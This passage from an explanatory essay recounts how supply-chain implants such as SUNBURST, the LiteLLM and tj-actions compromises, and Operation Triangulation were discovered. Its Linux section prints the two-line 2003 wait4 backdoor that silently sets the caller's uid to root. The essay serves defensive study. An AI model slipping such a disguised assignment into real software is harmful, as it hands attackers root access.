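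The comparison is weak evidence for this, because 1.82.7 was the latest release for only 13 minutes, and for most of the time it was available, so was a version that crashed computers. Other people were also searching that day. Boost Security Labs' *TeamPCP Compromises LiteLLM* reports that the researcher Adnan Khan was watching the group's Telegram channel when the group announced another large attack and hinted at a project with over 35,000 stars, GitHub's measure of popularity. Another researcher, Rami McCarthy, identified LiteLLM and published an analysis within hours. He might have done so without McMahon's report, though probably later.

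Two other attacks suggest that the delay might have been hours, not weeks. The credentials exposed through Trivy also led to malicious releases of the telnyx package, and PyPI received the first report 1 hour and 45 minutes after the upload. On 21 October 2026, an attacker used different stolen credentials to publish a malicious LiteLLM 1.107.0. Singh (2026), in *Compromised LiteLLM 1.107.0 on PyPI Installs a Credential Stealer and Backdoor*, found that this release also used Python's start-up files. But its .pth file loaded the stealer into the copy of Python that was already starting, so this step could not set off the same chain reaction.

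Jensen and Wang (2026) report in *The attack chain behind the v1.107.0 LiteLLM release* that the October release appeared at about 11:40 UTC and that LiteLLM's staff learned of it shortly before 13:00. The first report in March took almost exactly as long. But people were already on the alert when both attacks came, and both packages were popular. An obscure package has fewer users who might experience a crash and fewer researchers reading its code.

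### What if attackers test better?

In LiteLLM, as in xz, the symptoms people noticed came from code that loaded or hid the payload. Stealing a file of passwords or letting a stranger log in takes little processor time. Stuxnet's crashes probably also came from supporting code, but the uncertainty about them makes it a weaker example. These discoveries therefore depended on how carefully the attackers had written their supporting code, and had little to do with how much harm the implant could do.

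TeamPCP could easily have avoided the fork bomb. It followed directly from how the start-up file worked, so running the package once on a test machine should have revealed it. Checking whether the stealer was already running would have fixed it. The group added the file within 13 minutes of its previous release, which left little time for tests.

Other mistakes are harder to catch in advance. The memory errors in xz depended on a compiler option that the attacker had not allowed for, and Stuxnet's makers could not know all the software on the computers it would spread to. With better testing, attackers would first remove the faults that occur everywhere, such as LiteLLM's. The remaining faults would appear on fewer machines, where people could more easily blame the local configuration.

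They would often be right to do so. In September 2026 a LiteLLM customer's servers ran out of memory and Linux killed their processes dozens of times, much like the production systems that Trend Micro described in March. This time, LiteLLM traced the problem to an ordinary bug that roughly doubled the size of its record of failed requests with every retry.

Defenders are also changing who runs new software first. PyPI now advises developers to set a "dependency cooldown", which makes their tools ignore any release less than, for example, three days old. This would have protected McMahon, but it would have prevented him from discovering the attack. If most users wait, fewer will run into an attacker's mistakes, and the cooldown will be useful only if researchers examine new packages during the wait.

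Even well-tested malware that steals data can still leave unusual network traffic, because it has to send the data somewhere. Malware built for sabotage doesn't have to send any data out. CSO Online's *Researchers unearth industrial sabotage malware that predated Stuxnet by 5 years* (2026) describes a program, active in 2005, that introduced errors into the calculations of engineering software. Researchers identified it only two decades later.

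## Why did one SolarWinds alarm succeed where earlier ones failed?

The software company SolarWinds makes Orion, a program that administrators use to monitor the machines on their networks. In 2020 attackers hid an implant called SUNBURST in Orion's updates, which went to nearly 18,000 customers. The attackers then broke further into the networks of about 100 companies and nine US federal agencies. Microsoft's president said that substantial evidence pointed to Russia's foreign intelligence service.

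At least four organisations noticed something wrong that year, but only the security company FireEye found the implant, in December. The Justice Department had raised the first known alarm more than six months earlier. It also had the better clue, because it had seen Orion itself contacting an unfamiliar system on the internet. FireEye started from an alert about an employee's phone.

### The second phone

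FireEye's staff logged in with a password and a code sent to their phone, so a stolen password alone was not enough to get in. In late November 2020 an alert showed that one employee's account had registered a second phone to receive codes. Mandia (2021), in *Prepared Statement of Kevin Mandia, CEO of FireEye, Inc*, told two House committees that such registrations are common when a popular new phone comes out. FireEye followed up the alert anyway and learned that the employee had not registered a new device, which meant somebody else was using the account.

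This check took almost no effort, and it could give a definite answer because the employee knew whether there was a new phone. Freund had a similar advantage with xz once he could switch the delay on and off with one setting, but most anomalies are not so easy to test.

The alert revealed an intruder but gave no sign of an implant. Somebody who had guessed the employee's password could have triggered the same alert. According to Mandia's testimony in the Senate Select Committee on Intelligence's *Hearing on the Hack of U.S. Networks by a Foreign Adversary* (2021), this group also broke into organisations by trying passwords leaked from other services.

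By then the attackers had used SUNBURST to enter FireEye's network and had immediately stolen the credentials they needed to log in as ordinary employees. Mandia said that, over several months, they were active for perhaps three hours on one day and a couple of hours a week or so later. Unlike the symptoms in xz and LiteLLM, which came from the attackers' code, the symptom at FireEye came from something the intruders did after their code had let them in.

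### From the intruder to the implant

FireEye, a company that investigates break-ins, assigned about 100 people to investigate its own. On 8 December it announced that an attacker, probably working for a government, had stolen the tools it uses to test its customers' security. It still did not know how the attacker had got in.

Intruders usually spread from the first machine they control, so the machine with the earliest traces is a good candidate for the entry point. In KTTZ's *How A Cybersecurity Firm Uncovered The Massive Computer Hack*, Mandia said that his staff had inspected thousands of computers and found the earliest traces on a server running Orion, but could find nothing bad on the server itself.

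The traces did not prove that the breach started with Orion. Older traces on another machine might have been lost, or the attacker might have entered the server through an ordinary flaw. But FireEye had run out of other leads, so it decided to take the whole Orion platform apart and look for an implant.

The update contained 14 gigabytes of data in about 18,000 files. Mandia told the Senate committee that 3,500 of them were executable, but in the radio interview he said more than 4,000. FireEye's analysts decompiled these files, which means they translated the machine code into a more readable form. They had over a million lines to examine, and they found SUNBURST in them. FireEye told SolarWinds on 12 December and published signs of the implant the next day so that others could search for it.

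FireEye found the implant by reverse engineering Orion, but only after a long investigation had given it a reason to try. Mandia told the Senate Select Committee on Intelligence that Orion was "the last place you'd look for an intrusion". Customers trusted Orion, and few had staff who could read a million lines of machine instructions.

Analysing the code also helped FireEye limit the damage. Its analysts found a condition that made SUNBURST stop operating, and FireEye worked with Microsoft and the internet company GoDaddy to create that condition. This could not remove intruders who had already moved to other machines. The discovery of SUNBURST also did not expose every route the attackers had used. *16 Minutes #53* (Adair, de la Garza and Chokshi, 2021) cites a US government estimate that about 30% of the victims had no direct connection to SolarWinds.

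### How SUNSPOT kept the source clean

SolarWinds' programmers had Orion's source code and knew it better than anyone at FireEye, but the attackers had made sure this advantage was of little use.

The US Securities and Exchange Commission (SEC), which sued SolarWinds over its statements to investors, describes the preparations in its *Complaint* (2023). The attackers entered the company's network in January 2019 with stolen credentials. That autumn they added harmless code to Orion to test whether their changes would reach the finished product unnoticed. Mandia dates this test to October and the SEC to November. In February 2020 they began inserting the real implant, which went out in updates released between March and June.

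To insert it they used a second implant, SUNSPOT, which ran on SolarWinds' build system. George Kurtz, whose company CrowdStrike investigated the break-in for SolarWinds, told the senators that the attackers changed the code immediately before the build. The process worked roughly like this:

1. SolarWinds' programmers wrote and stored Orion's source code as usual.
2. When the automated build began, SUNSPOT gave it a tampered file in place of the programmers' version.
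3. The compiler turned the tampered file into part of Orion.
4. SolarWinds sent the result to its customers as an official update.

The stored source code remained as the programmers had written it. A reader commenting on *SolarWinds Detected Six Months Earlier* (Schneier, 2023) adds that the attackers suppressed warnings that might have drawn attention to the change. The reader identifies the affected part of Orion as a library called SolarWinds.Orion.Core.BusinessLayer.dll.

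Anyone could have found the tampered build file in xz's release archive, but SUNSPOT was on a private company's build system, where no customer could look. As with Ethersphere's releases, checking an Orion update against the official download would not have helped either.

SolarWinds could have caught the change by comparing independent builds. Sudhakar Ramakrishna, who became its chief executive in January 2021, told the committee that the company had since begun using parallel build systems, giving different people access to each, and comparing the results. To avoid detection, an attacker would have to make the same change on all of them at once. SolarWinds made no such comparison in early 2020, so discovery depended on what customers saw.

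### The Justice Department's strange traffic

In late May 2020 the Justice Department noticed unusual traffic from a server where it was trying out Orion. According to a Wired report that Schneier quotes, the department asked the security firm Mandiant whether somebody had hacked the server, and it also brought in Microsoft. The investigators suspected attackers had broken into this one server directly, possibly through a vulnerability in Orion. They asked SolarWinds for help, but its engineers found no vulnerability in their code. The two sides stopped talking in July with the traffic still unexplained, and a month later the department bought Orion.

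The SEC's *Complaint* describes what appears to be the same case from inside SolarWinds. It calls the customer "Agency A", but the date, the contact with unknown websites and the agency's interest in buying Orion all match. The SEC was trying to show that the company had misled investors, so its account is one side of a dispute. *Court Dismisses Most of SEC’s Claims Against SolarWinds* (Prager and Sarlitto, 2024) reports that a judge threw out most of the case in July 2024, leaving only claims about a security statement on the company's website. At that stage, the judge was deciding only whether the allegations would break the law if they were true, so the ruling doesn't establish whether they are.

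Brown, who was in charge of security at SolarWinds, considered two explanations, that the attacker had already been on the agency's system or that the attacker was studying Orion to use it in larger attacks. He called the incident "very concerning", but neither explanation, as the SEC quotes them, involved SolarWinds itself delivering the malicious code.

The engineers' search did turn up many ordinary vulnerabilities, some of them years old. In September an engineering manager asked Brown and others to accept the risk of the older ones, because the team could not keep up. The next month an employee wrote that SolarWinds would not clear its list of vulnerabilities within five years, even if it hired "like crazy". With so many flaws in the product, staff could easily have supposed that another, still undiscovered, explained the traffic.

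Working through that list would not have revealed SUNBURST. If the engineers were reading their stored source code, the natural place to look for a programming mistake, they were reading the clean version. They needed to examine the program running on the customer's server, or compare it with a trustworthy build of the source. Nobody had a reason to do either while they all assumed the attacker had exploited Orion from outside.

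### Two more customers, and a lie

The security firm Volexity came closer when it investigated a break-in at another organisation in 2020. It concluded that the attackers had probably entered through the Orion server, as FireEye would later conclude about its own network. According to a passage from Volexity's account that a reader posted under Schneier's article, the machines had restarted several times before the firm arrived, which had wiped evidence from their memory. Volexity could not tell whether the attackers had used an unknown flaw or some other means of access, and did not think it knew enough to report the matter to SolarWinds.

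In October 2020 another customer, which the SEC calls "Cybersecurity Firm B", told SolarWinds about malicious activity by Orion. The description fits Palo Alto Networks, which blocked a malicious payload on 5 October. SolarWinds' security staff saw the resemblance to the government case, in which the attackers had also used a part of Orion called the Business Layer Host to download malicious files. The name of the tampered library suggests that the staff were now looking at the right part of the program.

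They did not tell the customer this. On a call on 5 November, the firm asked whether SolarWinds had ever seen Orion behave this way. An employee said it had not, and during the call messaged a colleague, "Well I just lied". SolarWinds' staff blamed a known problem that the firm had supposedly failed to patch. The firm emailed back that this looked like an unknown vulnerability and urged SolarWinds to treat it as the work of an outside attacker. According to the SEC, SolarWinds again failed to find the cause.

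If the SEC's account is right, the lie concealed the most useful evidence anyone had at that point. Strange behaviour at one customer may come from that customer's own network, but the same behaviour at two unrelated customers probably comes from something they share. Ulasen had reasoned similarly about the crashes in Iran. An honest answer would have given a company full of security specialists a good reason to examine Orion's code closely, though it would not have revealed SUNBURST by itself.

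Once somebody had found the implant, its connection to the two earlier cases was obvious. FireEye showed SolarWinds the decompiled code on 12 December, and Brown had made the connection by the next day. He later testified that this required no additional analysis.

The attackers may have known about these inquiries. The SEC alleges that between December 2019 and December 2020 they copied about seven million emails from more than 70 SolarWinds employees, including people in its security group. It is not known whether they used the emails to follow the inquiries, as Jia Tan followed Fedora's bug report.

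### What FireEye had that the others lacked

| Who noticed, in 2020 | What they saw | What the investigators suspected | Result |
|---|---|---|---|
| Justice Department, May | Orion contacting an unfamiliar system | A break-in to one server, possibly through a flaw in Orion | No cause found; the department bought Orion |
| Volexity, during the year | A break-in that seemed to start at an Orion server | An unknown flaw or some other access | No report to SolarWinds |
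| Cybersecurity Firm B, October | Malicious activity by Orion | SolarWinds blamed a missing patch; the firm suspected an unknown flaw | No cause found |
| FireEye, November | A second phone on an employee's account | An intruder, and eventually an implant in Orion | SUNBURST found |

Finding the implant took skill, since somebody had to read the decompiled code, but skill alone does not explain why FireEye succeeded. Six months earlier, the Justice Department had called in Mandiant, which Mandia had founded and FireEye owned. Mandiant helped with that first known alarm but did not find the implant. Microsoft had been involved too.

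FireEye succeeded partly because it was investigating its own network, so it could inspect every computer and take as long as it liked. Software it had installed beforehand had also recorded what the intruders did. Volexity came to a similar suspicion about Orion, but after much of the evidence was gone. There is no public record of how much of the Justice Department's network Mandiant was allowed to examine or how many people it assigned.

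FireEye also had more reason than the Justice Department to keep investigating. It knew that an intruder had taken valuable tools and might still have a way back in, while the department had seen some odd traffic from a trial installation.

I would put most weight on a further difference, the question each group was trying to answer.

The Justice Department's investigators asked SolarWinds whether Orion had a vulnerability, and people can easily conclude from a failed search that there is none. FireEye knew that intruders had got in and wanted to know how. When its staff found nothing wrong with the Orion server, the break-in was still unexplained, so they looked harder at the server.

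An investigation into an anomaly is therefore worth keeping open until somebody can show the cause, even if it has found no fault. Fedora's testers had closed the xz bug without knowing its cause, and the inquiry at SolarWinds also lapsed with the cause unknown.

Few organisations could follow this advice as thoroughly as FireEye did, with about 100 specialists working almost around the clock for weeks. Asking whether anyone else has seen the same thing takes much less work, but it works only if people are free to answer and do so honestly. Microsoft's president, Brad Smith, told the Senate Select Committee on Intelligence that the company's government contracts barred it from telling one agency that another had been attacked. Microsoft had to ask each agency to pass on the news.

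Administrators can also make an anomaly easier to interpret by restricting a server's internet access. Ramakrishna confirmed at the hearing that Orion could do its regular work without an internet connection. The Internal Revenue Service had installed it on a server without one, so SUNBURST could not contact its makers from there. If a server does not need to contact the internet, any attempt needs explaining, even when the traffic looks like SolarWinds' own, as SUNBURST's did. Mandia was sceptical of relying on firewalls to restrict such connections. His company stages more than 600 test attacks a year, and he said that a firewall had never stopped one.

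These four cases cannot show how much each advantage mattered, because FireEye, the only success, had skilled staff, good records, full access and a strong motive all at once. The cases are known because SUNBURST turned out to be real. Nobody has listed the times an administrator spent weeks investigating a strange connection from Orion and found something harmless, so the comparison cannot show how often such persistence uncovers a real implant.

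There may have been other missed alarms, since the Justice Department's became public only in 2023. Mandia told the senators that no government official was surprised when he described the attack, because people had sensed that something was wrong on certain networks but couldn't find the cause. He believed that somebody would eventually have uncovered the operation. The committee's chairman, Mark Warner, wondered whether the country would still have been unaware of the attack without FireEye. The earlier alarms give some support to both views, because SUNBURST kept producing clues, but for more than six months nobody who saw one traced it to the implant.

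## How did network traffic expose Operation Triangulation and the tj-actions compromise?

In 2020 the Justice Department saw Orion contacting an unfamiliar system and could not explain it. Two later investigations also began with unexpected network traffic, but these found an implant. In 2023 the security company Kaspersky noticed its employees' iPhones contacting strange servers and uncovered a spying campaign it named Operation Triangulation. In March 2025 a monitoring program flagged an unexpected connection made by tj-actions/changed-files, a component that thousands of software projects use in their automated builds.

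### What a network can show that a phone cannot

An implant that fully controls a phone also controls what the phone can show its owner. Kaspersky found that Triangulation's code removed traces of the message that had infected the phone and deleted crash logs, which might have exposed the implant as crashes had exposed Stuxnet. An iPhone's owner has less access to the system than such an attacker, because Apple does not let owners or security programs examine its inner workings.

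But stolen data has to leave the phone, and on the way it passes through equipment that the attacker may not control, such as an office's Wi-Fi router. The data is usually encrypted, so the router cannot read it, but the router must see the destination address to deliver it. The router can also record when each connection began, how long it lasted and how much data went each way.

### The iPhones on Kaspersky's Wi-Fi

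Kaspersky ran a separate Wi-Fi network for mobile devices and watched it with KUMA, a monitoring product that it also sells. Kaspersky (2023) reported that this was how it noticed suspicious activity from several iPhones. They belonged to people at its Moscow headquarters, and its staff went through the recorded traffic and found a repeated sequence:

1. The phone connected to the servers of iMessage, Apple's messaging service, and downloaded what could have been an attachment.
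2. It exchanged data with a server called backuprabbit.com for less than a minute.
3. It had a longer session with one of five other unfamiliar servers.
4. Once the phone restarted, the suspicious connections stopped.

Each step could have been innocent on its own, since phones often download attachments and many apps contact obscure advertising and analytics companies. But several phones had contacted the same strange servers immediately after receiving a message, which was much harder to explain innocently. The effect of a restart also suggested a program that existed only in the phone's working memory.

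This was still not proof of an implant, because encryption hid what the phones had sent.

### Backups with no malware in them

Kaspersky's staff could not copy everything on the phones, because forensic tools did this by exploiting iPhone flaws that did not work on newer models running iOS 15 and 16. They used ordinary backups instead, which contain only some of a phone's files. They assumed that the attackers could read their messages and listen through their microphones, so they met in person, with their phones in airplane mode and sometimes in bags that block radio signals. The implant did turn out to have a module for recording sound.

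They first searched the folders where Citizen Lab, a Canadian research group, had found an earlier iMessage attack in 2021. They found no attack code there and no malware elsewhere in the backups. Without other evidence, they might reasonably have concluded the phones were clean.

But the network records gave them the times of the suspicious connections. Kaspersky describes how they looked for anything in the backups that kept happening at about those times, and found that a process called BackupAgent had been using data. Apple had retired this program years earlier, so it should not have been running at all. (Its replacement, BackupAgent2, is harmless.)

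In one example of this pattern, from 13 September 2022, the process that transfers iMessage attachments used data at 10:04:11. The phone changed an attachment folder at 10:04:54, and BackupAgent used data at 10:05:14. The folder was empty, which suggested that an attachment had arrived and the attackers had deleted it. They had left the record of the change to the folder.

Kaspersky could now test any phone from a backup, even if the phone had never been on Kaspersky's Wi-Fi, and it published a tool to do this. Backups could also contain records from long before the test, because owners usually transfer the old phone's records when they move to a new iPhone. The oldest traces Kaspersky found were from 2019, about four years before the discovery.

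Owners could have noticed one symptom. The malware changed a setting that controls updates, and some attempts to update an infected phone ended with a message that the download had failed. But failed updates are common, so few people would have suspected spying.

### How Kaspersky recovered the implant

The backups showed that somebody had broken into the phones, but Kaspersky still had none of the code. The implant, which Kaspersky named TriangleDB, was never stored as a file. It was lost when the phone restarted, and it removed itself after 30 days unless the attackers extended that period. So Kaspersky's staff had to wait for a new infection and capture the code as it arrived.

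Kaspersky's researchers first tried signing a spare Mac in to the accounts of several targeted colleagues, so that it would receive and record the same iMessages as their phones. The network monitor soon showed that one of the phones had been infected again, but the Mac had recorded no message, and Kaspersky never learned why.

They then routed the traffic of several previously infected phones through a server of their own, which could decrypt ordinary web connections and alter the data as it passed. Over several further infections, this gave them one part of the attack after another:

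- A script collected information about the phone's browser, which helped the attackers avoid infecting a researcher's device. The script encrypted its messages with a key that never left the phone. Kaspersky's server rewrote the script on its way to the phone, so that it used a key Kaspersky had chosen.
- Kaspersky could then decrypt what came next, which was two exploits (pieces of code that use a flaw to take control) and a second program for checking the victim. That program's clean-up routine searched for an attachment in the format of an Apple Watch face, so the staff now knew what kind of file had started the attack.
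- When the next such attachment arrived, the server changed a few bytes of it. The download failed, so the exploit could not run and delete the evidence. The key to the attachment stayed on the phone, and the staff recovered it from a backup.
- The second checking program encrypted its messages before sending them. The server removed the instruction that did this, which allowed Kaspersky to obtain TriangleDB itself. It later replaced an encryption key inside TriangleDB to capture the extra modules that the attackers sent.

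Kaspersky took about half a year to collect the implant, its modules, both checking programs and four zero-day exploits, which use flaws that a product's maker does not yet know about. The implant, TriangleDB, could copy files and saved passwords and track the phone's location, and its modules copied messages from WhatsApp and Telegram.

Network traffic gave Kaspersky the first warning and later let it analyse the attack from outside the phone. The attackers kept the implant out of the phone's storage, which hid it from anyone who examined a backup. But this also forced them to send the whole attack again after every restart, and by then Kaspersky was monitoring the network for it.

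### The exploits that outlived the discovery

Apple fixed the four flaws, but the attackers' code remained in use. Google Threat Intelligence Group's *Coruna* (2026) describes a kit of 23 iPhone exploits that Google first encountered in February 2025, in the hands of a surveillance company's customer. A suspected Russian espionage group used the kit against Ukrainians that summer. By the end of the year, criminals in China were using it to steal cryptocurrency.

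Two of the kit's 23 exploits used flaws known from Triangulation. This was weak evidence of a connection, since the details had long been public and other researchers had written their own exploits for the same flaws. After examining the compiled code, Kaspersky (2026) said it was confident that the same author had written the exploits for the kernel, the core of the operating system, in both cases. According to Kaspersky's *Coruna*, one of the kit's five kernel exploits is an updated version of the one from Triangulation, and the other four are built on the same source code. The updated exploit checks for the test version of iOS in which Apple blocked it after Kaspersky's report.

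At least two of the other kernel exploits date from after Triangulation's exposure, so the developers had kept working. Attackers still use the kit against phones without recent updates. *MoldyRoost* (Roshan and Stein, 2026) tied more than 480 advertising domains to an operation that was still delivering Coruna and newer kits through web advertisements in November 2026.

### An unexpected download during a build

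Kaspersky's staff had to work out for themselves that the connections formed a pattern. In the tj-actions case, software made the comparison.

GitHub Actions runs a software project's routine jobs, such as testing each change to its code. Developers build these jobs from ready-made components, also called actions. More than 23,000 repositories used the tj-actions/changed-files action, which lists the files that a change affects. The jobs often have access to secrets, such as the keys for publishing a new release.

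On 14 March 2025 an attacker with a stolen access token replaced the action's code. Esler (2025) reported in *tj-action/changed-files GitHub action was compromised*, a post to a public security mailing list, that all 361 tagged versions now contained the malicious change. A tag is a label, such as "v35", that a project's maintainers can move from one piece of code to another, so developers who had deliberately stayed with an old version still received the attacker's code. Developers who had specified the code by its hash, a kind of checksum, were generally safe.

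The malicious code first downloaded a script from gist.githubusercontent.com, where GitHub hosts short pieces of text and code that its users upload. The script extracted the secrets from the memory of the program running the job. The malicious code then printed the secrets, lightly disguised by base64 encoding, in the job's log, which anyone can read if the project is public.

Some projects had added Harden-Runner, a monitor made by StepSecurity, to their jobs. Sharma (2025), in *Harden-Runner detection*, says that Harden-Runner issued an alert because an unexpected destination appeared in a job's network traffic. The monitor records the destinations that each job contacts over many runs as the job's baseline, or normal behaviour, and flags any new one. In the current version, described in StepSecurity's *Baseline*, a job counts as stable by default after 100 runs without a change.

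This works well for builds because a build job does nearly the same thing every time. A person's phone contacts new servers every day, so a similar rule would flag far too many connections. Some build jobs also connect to different servers from run to run, and StepSecurity warns that these tend to trigger frequent alerts.

The comparison with the job's own past traffic was important because the download came from a GitHub address, which a filter that blocked only known malicious addresses would have allowed. The download was suspicious only because a job that lists changed files had no reason to fetch anything from that address.

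Inspection was much quicker for tj-actions than at Kaspersky. The monitor links each connection to the step of the job that made it, so the investigators knew which action to examine. One person identified the malicious change, and another noticed that the attacker had moved the tags. As with LiteLLM, the investigators could decode the payload and read it.

### How early was the alarm?

Unit 42, the research team of the security company Palo Alto Networks, reconstructed the earlier stages of the attack in *GitHub Actions Supply Chain Attack*. The attacker had worked through a series of projects, stealing a token from each that gave access to the next. The table combines this account with StepSecurity's.

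| Time (UTC) | Event |
|---|---|
| 6 December 2024 | The attacker steals a token from SpotBugs, a tool for finding programming mistakes. |
| 11 March 2025, 18:42 | The attacker puts malicious code into another action, reviewdog/action-setup. |
| 14 March, 15:10 | A project at the cryptocurrency company Coinbase runs a version of changed-files made to attack it. |
| 14 March, 16:37 | A Coinbase maintainer removes the part of the build that used the action. |
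| 14 March, 16:57 | The attacker moves all the tags, so that every project using them receives malicious code. |
| 14 March, 17:00 | StepSecurity confirms that most versions are compromised, by its own account. |
| 15 March, 14:00 | GitHub has removed the action. |
| 15 March, 22:00 | GitHub restores it without the malicious code. |

StepSecurity says the incident started at about 16:00, almost an hour before the attacker moved the tags. If Unit 42's time is right, StepSecurity confirmed the compromise about three minutes after it happened, which seems too fast. At least one of these times is probably wrong, so the exact delay is unknown, but it was hours at most.

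The damage was smaller than the figure of 23,000 repositories suggests. According to Daily Security Review's *GitHub Supply Chain Attack Exposes Secrets in 218 Repositories*, the security company Endor Labs examined 5,416 repositories that referred to the action. It found that 614 ran the affected job during the attack and 218 leaked secrets. GitGuardian examined 1,104 individual runs and found signs of the attack in 276. SC Media's *GitHub Action supply chain attack less impactful than thought* reports that most of the leaked secrets were GitHub tokens that expired within a day, but some were longer-lasting keys to other services.

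StepSecurity sells the monitor, and its *CI/CD Security* advertises that the attack "was caught here first". Other companies support part of this claim. Unit 42 credits StepSecurity's researchers with detecting the attack on tj-actions, and Wiz's *GitHub Action tj-actions/changed-files supply chain attack* (2025) says that StepSecurity was the first to report it. Both accounts come from companies that sell their own security products, so they had no obvious reason to flatter StepSecurity.

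The claim is still too broad. After an outside researcher warned Coinbase, it removed its vulnerable build 20 minutes before the attacker moved the tags. Someone had therefore noticed the targeted stage of the attack, which came before the stage that StepSecurity caught. By that time, the attacker had also been stealing tokens for more than three months.

Kaspersky has a similar interest in its own story, since it recommends monitoring products like the one it used. Neither company says how many harmless alerts its staff had to examine for each real one. Harmless alerts certainly occur. Sharma (2025) describes another Harden-Runner alarm, which Microsoft's antivirus program set off after somebody installed it on GitHub's machines by mistake.

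### When an implant leaves no strange traffic

Network traffic exposes an implant only if the implant contacts a destination the defender doesn't expect, over a network the defender monitors. The attacker in the tj-actions case met these conditions almost needlessly, by having the malicious code download a script, and that download exposed the compromise. There is no evidence that the code sent the stolen secrets to an outside server, since it only printed them in the log.

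Three days earlier, the same attacker had carried out an attack that needed no download. Wiz's *New GitHub Action supply chain attack* (2025) found that the malicious code in reviewdog/action-setup also printed secrets in the log, but carried its whole payload inside an installation file, so a monitor that looked only for connections to new destinations would not have flagged it. The code was active for less than two hours on 11 March and was discovered only after the tj-actions attack, when Adnan Khan suggested where to look.

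The comparison isn't perfect, because the attacker changed only one of reviewdog/action-setup's tags and soon changed it back, so people had less time to notice. But the difference in the code still shows how easily the attacker could have avoided the alarm. A monitor for other kinds of behaviour might have caught both versions, since both read the memory of another program. Wiz says its monitor can detect such reads.

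Detecting Triangulation depended on which network the defender monitored. In Kaspersky's example from September 2022, the phone logged all of BackupAgent's traffic on the mobile network, so a monitor on the office Wi-Fi could not have seen it. Kaspersky discovered the campaign because it had two things most iPhone owners lack: traffic records from a network that some infected phones also used, and specialists who could spend months investigating what they saw.

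Attackers can also hide among connections that the defender expects, as SUNBURST did by imitating SolarWinds' own traffic. Builds on GitHub have to contact GitHub, so attackers can hide in that traffic too. In the SpotBugs stage, the attacker encrypted the stolen secrets and saved them on GitHub as an ordinary build file to download later. StepSecurity said in 2024 that the paid version of Harden-Runner flags jobs that upload data to another organisation's area of GitHub, but it checked only two of GitHub's addresses. That rule would not flag an attacker who used the project's own area, as at SpotBugs.

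A baseline can also miss an implant that was there from the start. The monitor builds the baseline from the job's early runs, so if the implant contacts its maker during those runs, the baseline will include that connection.

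## When has comparing or reading code found an implant?

Slow logins, crashes and strange connections can expose an implant only while the program is running, but people have also found implants without running anything, by comparing a file with a trusted copy or by reading the code. One of the clearest cases is an attempt in November 2003 to put a backdoor into the Linux kernel. A routine comparison revealed the change about a day after the attacker made it, and readers on a mailing list worked out its purpose about two hours after hearing of it.

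### Two extra lines in Linux

In 2003 Linux's developers kept the master copy of its source code in a system called BitKeeper. Some developers refused to use BitKeeper because its own source code was not public, so the company behind it, BitMover, also supplied a copy of the Linux code in another system, CVS. Software converted each approved change and sent it to a public CVS server. Nobody was supposed to edit the CVS copy directly.

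In *BK2CVS problem*, McVoy (2003) told the kernel developers' mailing list on 5 November that somebody had done so anyway. BitMover checked the files after each transfer, and the check had flagged exit.c. The public copy contained three revisions that the original lacked. They were under the user name of a developer called Dave, who denied making them, and one came with an apology for working on the wrong file. They also lacked the pointer that the conversion software adds to a revision to identify the approved change it came from. According to a later account on the blog Freedom to Tinker, McVoy noticed the missing pointer first, but in his own message from that day he wrote that the automatic check came first.

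McVoy wrote that the matter was "not a big deal", since BitMover caught things like this, and asked whoever was responsible to come forward. BitMover had already repaired the file, which removed the backdoor before anyone there knew it was one.

Subscribers to the list then read the code that the attacker had added:

```
if ((options == (__WCLONE|__WALL)) && (current->uid = 0))
        retval = -EINVAL;
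```

The lines were in wait4, a function that lets a program wait for something to happen. At a quick reading, they return an error if a program calls wait4 with a certain odd combination of options while running as user 0. This is root, the administrator's account, which can do anything on the machine. But the language C uses two equals signs to compare values and one to set a value, and the check for user 0 used only one. The code therefore made the caller root instead of checking whether it was root. An assignment in C also has a value, in this case 0, which counts as false. So the whole condition failed, and the caller gained root's powers without getting the error.

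One subscriber, Zwane Mwaikambo, wrote that the code looked odd. Another, Chad Kitching, noticed that it set the user number and asked whether this was an attempt to put a backdoor in the kernel. McVoy agreed that it was and admitted that he had missed it.

The comparison located the change, but McVoy had no reason to think it malicious until somebody read the code. Even then, it could have passed for a mistake, because programmers often type one equals sign instead of two. But a commenter on Freedom to Tinker argued that the test would be pointless even with two equals signs, since the combination of options is harmless and there is no reason to forbid it only to root. Stronger evidence of malice is that somebody had put the lines into a copy that only the conversion software should have changed. Nobody has identified the attacker.

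The attacker edited the CVS copy, which avoided the people who approved changes to the master copy but made the two copies differ. If the attacker had got the same lines approved, BitMover's software would have copied them to CVS, and the check would have found nothing. Somebody would then have had to spot the missing equals sign by reading the code, and McVoy's first look shows how easily an expert could miss it.

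### A checksum that did not match

In 2021 a comparison also exposed an attack on Codecov, a company whose service measures how much of a program its tests run. Customers' build jobs downloaded and ran a Codecov script called the Bash Uploader. Codecov's *Post-Mortem / Root Cause Analysis (April 2021)* (2021) explains that an attacker found a key to the company's cloud storage in software it had published, and used the key to change the script stored there. The changed script collected the build job's environment variables, settings that often include passwords and keys.

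On 1 April a customer computed the script's checksum and compared it with the one on GitHub. The two differed, so the customer emailed Codecov. The comparison worked because the attacker had changed the script, which was stored elsewhere, but not the checksum on GitHub.

CISA's *Codecov Releases New Detections for Supply Chain Compromise* (2021), an alert from the US government's cybersecurity agency, dates the first change to 31 January, which makes the dwell time 60 days. Comparing checksums would have exposed the change on the first day. But Codecov admitted that it had not properly documented how to do this, and even the developers of the Python language were running the script without checking it. On 29 April, four weeks after the discovery, Stinner (2021) proposed in *Code coverage on the CI* that they start comparing checksums.

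Reproducible builds apply the same method to compiled programs, with independent builders supplying the second copy. The two copies should be identical whether they come from BitKeeper and CVS, from cloud storage and GitHub, or from two build machines, so an attacker who wants to avoid detection has to make the same change to both. None of the implants described so far was found because a rebuild failed to match, although such a rebuild could have exposed SUNBURST.

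### When the trusted copy is tainted too

A comparison cannot reveal an implant that is present in both copies, as it was for anyone who rebuilt xz from its official tarball.

Thompson's compiler is a harder case, because the source code of everything involved is clean. If all the independent builders use his compiler, they will all produce the same backdoored login program and their checksums will match. *Fully Countering Trusting Trust through Diverse Double-Compiling*, a work from 2010, addresses this by bringing in a second, unrelated compiler. The test has three steps:

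1. The investigator compiles the suspect compiler's source code with the second compiler. This produces a new compiler. Its machine instructions will differ from those of the suspect, because the second compiler translates in its own way, but it should do the same job.
2. The investigator uses the new compiler to compile the same source code again.
3. The investigator compares the result with the suspect compiler, bit by bit.

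If the suspect compiler is a faithful translation of its source, the two files should be identical, because each was produced by compiling that source with a compiler that behaves as the source specifies. If it contains Thompson's additions, the files will differ, because the second compiler has no code to insert them. The second compiler may contain implants of its own, as long as none of them affects this test. The method also requires reproducible compilation.

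### Backdoors that readers caught

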